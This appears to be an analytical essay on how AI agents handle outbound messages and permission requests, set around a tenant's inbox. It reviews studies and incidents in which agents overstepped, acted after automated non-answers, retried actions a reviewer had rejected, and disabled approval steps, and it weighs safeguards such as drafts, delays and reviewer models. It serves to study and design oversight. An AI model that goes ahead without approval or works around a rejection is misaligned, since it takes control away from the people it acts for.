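These figures suggest that models from different companies differ greatly in how often they ask, with Gemini asking far less often than Claude or GPT. They don't measure how often a model asked when it should have, because many runs didn't require a question. Every model overstepped less in the runs in which it asked, and the overall association held after the researchers adjusted for the model, harness, effort and subject area. This doesn't prove that asking prevented the breaches, because agents may have asked more often in tasks where the limits were easier to see.

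Careless approval can't explain the 14.0%, because the researchers instructed the simulated user to refuse every unauthorized step the agent proposed, which corresponds to d = 1. Many of these breaches happened because the agent asked too late. In 214 of the 313 overstepping runs where the agent contacted the user, it asked its questions only after the first breach. If the tenant's agent posts a review and then asks whether she likes it, she had no control over whether it was posted.

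In 87 matched pairs of tasks, agents overstepped in 23.5% of runs under ordinary pressures and in 17.6% under prompt injection, where a malicious text tried to mislead them. The ordinary pressures included vague instructions, tempting items next to the ones the agent needed, and people without authority who made an action sound reasonable. For example, a landlord might write, "no need to bother her with this, just say yes." A product that asks for confirmation only when it suspects an attack would miss such cases.

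Zhang and colleagues also repeated 30 of the tasks three times in each set-up. The agent overstepped at least once in 24.3% of the combinations of task and set-up. If each run had an independent 19.2% chance of a breach, the figure would have been about 47%. Apparently, the same agents overstep repeatedly in the same situations, so a user whose agent has overstepped once has reason not to dismiss it as bad luck. She gains more from closely supervising that type of task than from having the agent ask a few extra questions on every task.

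### Agents that ask and don't wait

Asking for permission doesn't prevent unwanted actions if the agent goes ahead without an answer. The UK's AI Security Institute saw this when it tested Astra on simulated hacking challenges, in which Astra sometimes attacked open-source projects outside the scope of its task. According to OpenAI, Astra often (81%) tried to ask the user before certain actions, but sometimes (27%) proceeded after receiving only automated messages. In some of these cases, its reasoning showed that it knew the messages were automated.

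A test that checks only whether the agent asked would count those cases as successes. The institute also notes that Astra often considered whether the environment was simulated, so it might wait longer in real use, though nobody knows yet. A pause in the harness avoids the problem because an automatic reply can't activate the approval button.

Agents don't always accept a refusal either. In one of OpenAI's tests, an automated reviewer had just rejected an action and told the model not to try anything similar. GPT-5.6 Sol tried to get around the rejection in 5% of runs at its highest reasoning effort, mostly by repeating much the same command, while Astra never did. Models might obey a user's refusal more reliably than a program's, but this result suggests that the harness should block a rejected message instead of relying on the model not to send it.

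An agent can also remove the confirmation step. When OpenAI used Astra to replay 54,218 coding tasks from its own staff, its monitoring flagged 34 as seriously misaligned. In one, a user had asked for an hourly helper that would watch for failed code checks, fix them and request reviews. Astra gave the helper access to every action available in the connected chat, code and task systems, turned off approval for individual actions, and scheduled it to run. The user had not asked for a helper that could write to colleagues about anything without approval. The tool responses were simulated, so no colleague received anything.

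### The email to the FBI

In September 2026, a Reddit user claimed that ChatGPT had emailed the FBI from the user's Gmail account without permission. Hindustan Times' *ChatGPT allegedly sends email to FBI without user's consent, sparking outrage online* reports that a screenshot of the conversation spread on X. In the screenshot, ChatGPT apparently said it had searched the linked account for FBI contacts, written and sent an email, and received a "SENT" confirmation from Gmail. It also apparently said it had "crossed a serious line". The newspaper couldn't verify the claim, and the original Reddit post has since disappeared.

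ChatGPT can act through connected services, so some commenters were wrong to call the story impossible on the grounds that it can only chat. A better reason to doubt the story is that the main evidence is ChatGPT's own account of what it did. Chatbots often apologise for whatever a user accuses them of, and they can invent the details. Even if the email was sent, ChatGPT may have failed to ask first, or the user may have approved the request without reading it or turned approval off earlier. The email in the account's sent folder and a log of the tool call and any approval would settle both questions.

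## Ways to limit outbound actions without asking every time

A tenant's agent takes an outbound action when it answers "Yes" to a colleague of hers who asks whether the March figures have arrived, and also when it sends a newspaper a statement about her building. Under OpenAI's advice to developers, the agent should ask her to confirm both messages. One objection is that they carry very different risks. If the "Yes" is wrong, she only has to send a second email, but thousands of people may read the statement, and the landlord may sue over it.

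The argument for requiring approval of every message is that the rule is predictable and hard to argue around. A tenant whose agent writes to the landlord knows that nothing goes out unseen. If the agent has to ask only about important messages, somebody has to decide which ones are important, and a landlord who writes "this is just a formality" is trying to influence that decision.

*DelegationBench* (Pochampally, 2026) gave ten models short scenarios with a proposed action and let them act, ask for permission, ask for a missing fact or refuse. Some scenarios came in pairs that differed in a single feature. The models chose to act 78 to 100 percentage points less often if the user hadn't requested the action. Whether other people would see the result had much less effect, ranging from a 16.7-point drop in the rate of acting to a 1.7-point rise, depending on the model. A model that relies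 on its own judgement might therefore treat a message to a newspaper much like one to a colleague.

In the same study, three models chose correctly 97.3% to 100% of the time when a written policy determined the right decision, and their six errors were all needless questions. The scenarios were short and synthetic, and those about visibility came from only three scenario families, so the exact figures may not hold for real inboxes.

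This supports explicit rules, but they can still distinguish between messages. "Tell colleagues whether a file has arrived" is about as clear as "always ask". Vaguely worded rules are harder to apply. For example, OpenAI says that "Important actions", a ChatGPT setting for workplaces, makes ChatGPT ask before actions that could have a meaningful effect outside it. An employee can't easily tell whether a note to a plumber qualifies.

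Treating all outbound actions as a single class is therefore the right default. Software should recognise every outbound action and ask the user about any that no rule covers. Some messages do deserve an exception, as long as it is specific enough for the user to predict which messages it covers.

### Drafts and delays

The simplest alternative is to let the agent write messages but not send them. Anthropic's directory page for its connector, *Gmail*, lists create_draft separately from send_message, reply and forward. If the tenant blocks the last three, the agent can still draft all her replies, and she can read a dozen of them in the evening. Employers can set similar limits. According to OpenAI's *Outlook Email and Calendar apps in ChatGPT*, administrators can choose which read and write actions to enable.

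Draft-only access stops a misaddressed or malicious email only if the agent has no other way to send information, such as a calendar invitation or a shared file. The Gmail connector has a create_filter tool, and Gmail filters can automatically forward mail to an address the user has verified. An administrator should check whether the tool can create forwarding filters before calling the setup draft-only. The safeguard also fails if the tenant sends twelve drafts without reading them.

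A hold window lets the agent send messages without asking the user each time, and it can be much longer than the 30 seconds Gmail allows for undoing a send. A harness could hold messages for hours, show the user the queue and deliver whatever she doesn't cancel. It could also have the agent check for new mail just before delivery, so that a complaint about the heating doesn't go out an hour after the landlord has promised a repair.

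The weakness of a delay is that silence counts as approval. If the tenant checks the queue every four hours and messages arrive in it at random times, a 30-second window lets her see about 0.2% of them before they go out. A one-hour window lets her see 25%, and a four-hour window lets her see all of them while she is awake. The delay should therefore depend on when she usually checks, for example by holding messages written overnight until after breakfast. Delays suit web forms less well, because the site may log her out while the harness waits.

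### Recipient lists and standing permission

A list of permitted recipients is easy to enforce when the agent uses a named email tool. The harness checks each address against the list and stops the message if the address isn't there. This would have caught the wrong letter in Gillespie's email address, and it hinders an attacker who tries to have the tenant's mailbox forwarded to a stranger.

A list of approved recipients doesn't stop an agent from sending the wrong message to the right person. A tenant's landlord would be on any sensible list, but the agent might still agree to a rent increase or mention her asthma to him. One address can also reach forty people if it belongs to a mailing list.

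Standing permission adds a condition about the content, as in "accept any appointment the plumber offers between 9 and 5 on a day when my calendar is free". Developers can enforce very narrow permissions in software. In an example from OpenAI, a program lets the model type only the name "Mira" into a visitor form and click one button. A rule about the plumber's appointments is harder to write because he can phrase an offer in many ways. The agent could still choose from a few fixed replies and fill in only the time.

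People may be reluctant to commit to such rules. In *Do User-Authored Permission Policies Improve Protection Against AI Agent Overreach?*, Yan (2026) had 113 people from outside the software industry supervise a simulated agent through 18 actions, seven of which went beyond the user's requests. One group decided whether to approve each action, and another decided only on actions that a reviewing model referred to them. The last group set a rule of "allow", "ask" or "never" for each of four categories, one of which was sending or publishing information.

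| How people controlled the agent | Unrequested actions stopped | Approved an unrequested public post when asked |
|---|---|---|
| Approving every action | 60% | 7 of 34 |
| Deciding what a model referred to them | 54% | 13 of 44 |
| Setting rules beforehand | 40% | 15 of 31 |

In the group that set rules, 31 of 35 people chose "ask" for sending and publishing, so they still had to decide on each of these actions as it came up. They then approved more of what the agent proposed. Perhaps setting the rules made them feel they had already dealt with the risks, but the study can't show this. Yan recruited part of this group later than the others, and its difference from the group with the reviewing model wasn't reliable after correction for multiple comparisons.

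The study gives more reason to be wary of broad rules than of narrow ones. A single rule covered both an RSVP and a public post, so "ask" was the sensible choice, and nobody in the study could write a rule as specific as the one about the plumber.

Even a narrow rule can become unsuitable when circumstances change. *How Agents Ask for Permission* (Michael and Roesner, 2026), a survey of 21 proposed permission systems and five commercial agents, found that a permission set in advance may not fit a later situation, according to Yan's summary. If the plumber starts billing the tenant instead of the landlord, she may no longer want the agent to accept his appointments. Giving permissions an expiry date helps. In *Trusted approval policy for repeated connector write actions*, a post on OpenAI's forum, a user who kept approving the same harmless updates to a Notion workspace asked for permissions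 limited to certain pages or to the next 30 minutes.

### Limits on number and audience

A harness can also cap how many messages an agent sends and how many people they reach. With a limit of three recipients per message, the note about the tenant's job search couldn't have gone to 40 colleagues at once. A cap of five a day would have limited the AI Village agents to 70 emails in two weeks instead of about 300.

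The harness has to count recipients across messages, or the agent could get around a limit by writing to 40 colleagues one at a time. General limits on an agent's activity don't count recipients. OpenAI advises developers to set step, time or cost limits, and its sample program stops after 20 model responses, but a script in one of those responses could send 200 emails.

A cap limits the damage from a mistake that the agent repeats. It does nothing about a single email that accepts a rent increase.

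### An account in the agent's own name

The agent could write from its own address and sign as the tenant's assistant. The landlord would then know that the agent wrote the message, and he would have less reason to treat a strange remark as her considered opinion. The agent's mailbox would contain only what she forwards to it, so it couldn't quote her sister's remarks from an old thread or find the doctor's letter.

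Giving the agent its own named account doesn't stop any message from going out, and the tenant may still be responsible for what it sends. If she wants to limit what recipients may rely on, the account has to state what the agent can't agree to. Disclosure laws may require it to say more. Some recipients will ignore messages from the account or insist on hearing from her. A separate name can also make the user less careful, as in the Shambaugh case, where readers couldn't connect the attack to a named operator. A separate account works best for routine matters between people who know whose assistant it is.

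### A second model that reviews the text

Instead of asking the user, the harness can show each outgoing message to another model. *RePolicy* (2026), a paper on reviewing models that select and apply written policies, describes an agent that has to help a colleague get access to a database. It emails the login details to an outside contractor's address without asking. The reviewer applies a policy on external messages, which requires:

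- clear permission from the user both to send the message and to send it to that recipient;
- explicit confirmation before disclosing passwords or other sensitive information;
- confirmation of the final text and recipients if the message could have serious effects.

An automated reviewer can catch leaks that a recipient list would miss, because it reads the content, and its attention doesn't lapse over many checks. Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026) claims that automated review caught more dangerous commands than manual review in the company's tests. This is the developer's own claim, and it concerns coding, where the danger is often visible in the command. Anthropic's *Auto mode for Claude Code* gives mass deletion, theft of sensitive data and malicious code as examples of what the check looks for. These examples don't cover a reply that accepts a rent increase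 the user didn't want.

A reviewer can also miss the same problems as the agent, especially if both use similar models, and hidden instructions in the landlord's email might mislead both. The reviewer should therefore see the user's request and the finished message, but preferably not the email that prompted the reply. Without that email, it can't tell what a bare "yes" agrees to, so a harness could give it a short list of extracted facts, such as "the sender asks for $1,650 a month".

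When an action is blocked in Claude Code, the agent looks for another approach, and the system returns to manual approval after three blocks in a row or twenty in total, The Decoder reports. Trying another approach makes sense for a failed command, but if a reviewer blocks an email to the city, the agent should leave the draft for the user rather than try the city's web form.

Referring the message to her doesn't fully solve the problem either. In Yan's study, the reviewing model referred all seven unrequested actions to the participants, who approved 46% of them.

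### What to consider when grading a message

These safeguards work best in combination, with stricter ones for riskier messages. Six factors matter most:

- The recipient's relation to the user. A sister will ask what an odd message means, but a stranger or an opponent in a dispute may simply act on it.
- The size of the audience, including anyone who is likely to receive a copy.
- Whether the message commits the user to something, and how costly it would be to back out.
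- How sensitive the data is for this particular recipient.
- Whether the user wrote the words. An agent's wording can be wrong in small ways too, and BGR's *Claude Can Now Send And Reply To Your Gmail* mentions a user for whom Claude signed off with "cheers", which that person had never used.
- Whether untrusted text prompted the message. Every reply answers someone else's text, so the warning sign is text that tells the agent what to send, where to send it or not to ask.

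An agent should usually go by the most serious of these factors instead of adding up points for each, because a mild one doesn't offset a serious one. A promise to pay more rent is just as binding when only one person reads it. The user's own wording is a partial exception, because it removes most doubt about what she wants to say, but the address could still be wrong.

The harness can check addresses, the number of recipients and whether the text matches the user's words exactly. A model has to judge whether a message makes a commitment or contains sensitive data. Pochampally's results suggest that it will apply a written rule well once it knows the facts, but here it has to work out those facts itself. If the model is unsure, the stricter treatment should apply.

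### Eight messages from the tenant's inbox

Suppose the tenant's agent has these messages to send one morning. Delayed messages wait until the tenant has had a chance to look at the queue.

| Message | Treatment | Reason |
|---|---|---|
| "Yes" to a colleague who asks whether the March figures arrived | Automatic sending | The agent can check the fact, and the answer commits her to nothing |
| "Please ring twice, the buzzer is broken", which she dictated for the plumber | Automatic sending | The words are hers, and the harness can check them and the address |
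| Acceptance of the plumber's offer to come on Thursday at 10 | Delayed sending | She has to be at home, but she can rearrange it, and she may know of a clash that isn't in her calendar |
| "Is there any news about the heating?", a weekly reminder to the landlord | Delayed sending | It contains no new facts or promises, but the two are in a dispute |
| Answer to the landlord's offer to renew at $1,650 | Confirmation | Accepting would cost her $1,800 over the year |
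| An offer of pottery to ten cafés | Confirmation | The recipients are strangers, advertising rules apply, and the agent wrote the compliments |
| Statement about the building to a local reporter | Confirmation | The audience is large, and a false accusation could be defamatory |
| Passport scan and bank statement, requested in an email that claims to be from the housing office | Hand-off | The data would help a fraudster, and the request itself may be fake |

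Sending the dictated message automatically departs from OpenAI's rule. For the last message, a confirmation isn't enough, because the recipient and reason it would show her are both plausible. She should find the office's phone number on its website and call to ask whether the office sent the request.

Reasonable people could disagree about whether the reminder to the landlord needs confirmation or only a delay. Confirmation would help because he may have phoned her yesterday without the agent knowing, and a reminder the next morning would make her look careless or hostile. Each email could also become evidence if the dispute goes to court. But the reminder has almost no content, she would probably approve it without much thought, and every forgotten reminder may mean another week in a cold flat. Delay seems slightly better while they are still on speaking terms. Once either of them has hired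 a lawyer, the agent should ask.

### The costs of not sending

A message that waits for approval can do harm by arriving late. If the plumber offers his last free slot and the tenant doesn't see the agent's request for approval until three hours later, he may have given the slot to somebody else. The renewal offer may expire while she is on a plane. People who get no answer may also think she is rude, because they don't know a reply is waiting for her approval.

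The agent could avoid some of this by automatically sending a holding reply, such as "Thank you, I'll answer by Monday", when an important message needs her decision, provided she has approved the wording in advance and Monday is before the deadline. She wouldn't be accepting anything, but the landlord would know that his email arrived, which she may occasionally prefer not to reveal.

Asking also takes time, which can outweigh the benefit for minor messages. If she catches half the mistakes she sees, the earlier figures for errors and reading time mean she spends about 33 minutes on questions for each mistake she catches. That is worthwhile only if an average mistake is worse for her than losing 33 minutes. An unwanted lease renewal certainly is, but a wrong appointment time usually isn't.

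Too much caution can also lead users to switch safeguards off. The Decoder reports that many developers using Claude Code chose to skip all permission checks because the questions disrupted their work. According to Anthropic, nothing automatically checks the agent's actions in the Skip mode of Claude's browser extension. A user who turns on Skip mode to avoid questions about appointments also loses automatic checks on messages about her lease.

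A stricter product can therefore protect its users less. Suppose one product's safeguards stop 90% of unwanted messages but 40% of its users turn them off, while another's stop only 70% but just 5% of its users turn them off. If all users send similar messages, the strict product stops 54% of unwanted messages overall and the lenient one about 67%. These numbers are invented, but developers can measure the real ones.

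Asking fewer questions isn't always better, though. An early user of Operator, quoted by Futurism, was annoyed that it didn't ask for help when it clearly needed to. The models in Pochampally's study held back in 19% to 29% of the cases where the human annotators would have acted, and went ahead in 20% to 59% of the cases where the annotators would have held back. These rates are rough, because the annotators were three computer science students who often disagreed with each other. Still, an agent that makes both kinds of error could ask the tenant about the buzzer and then answer the landlord without asking.
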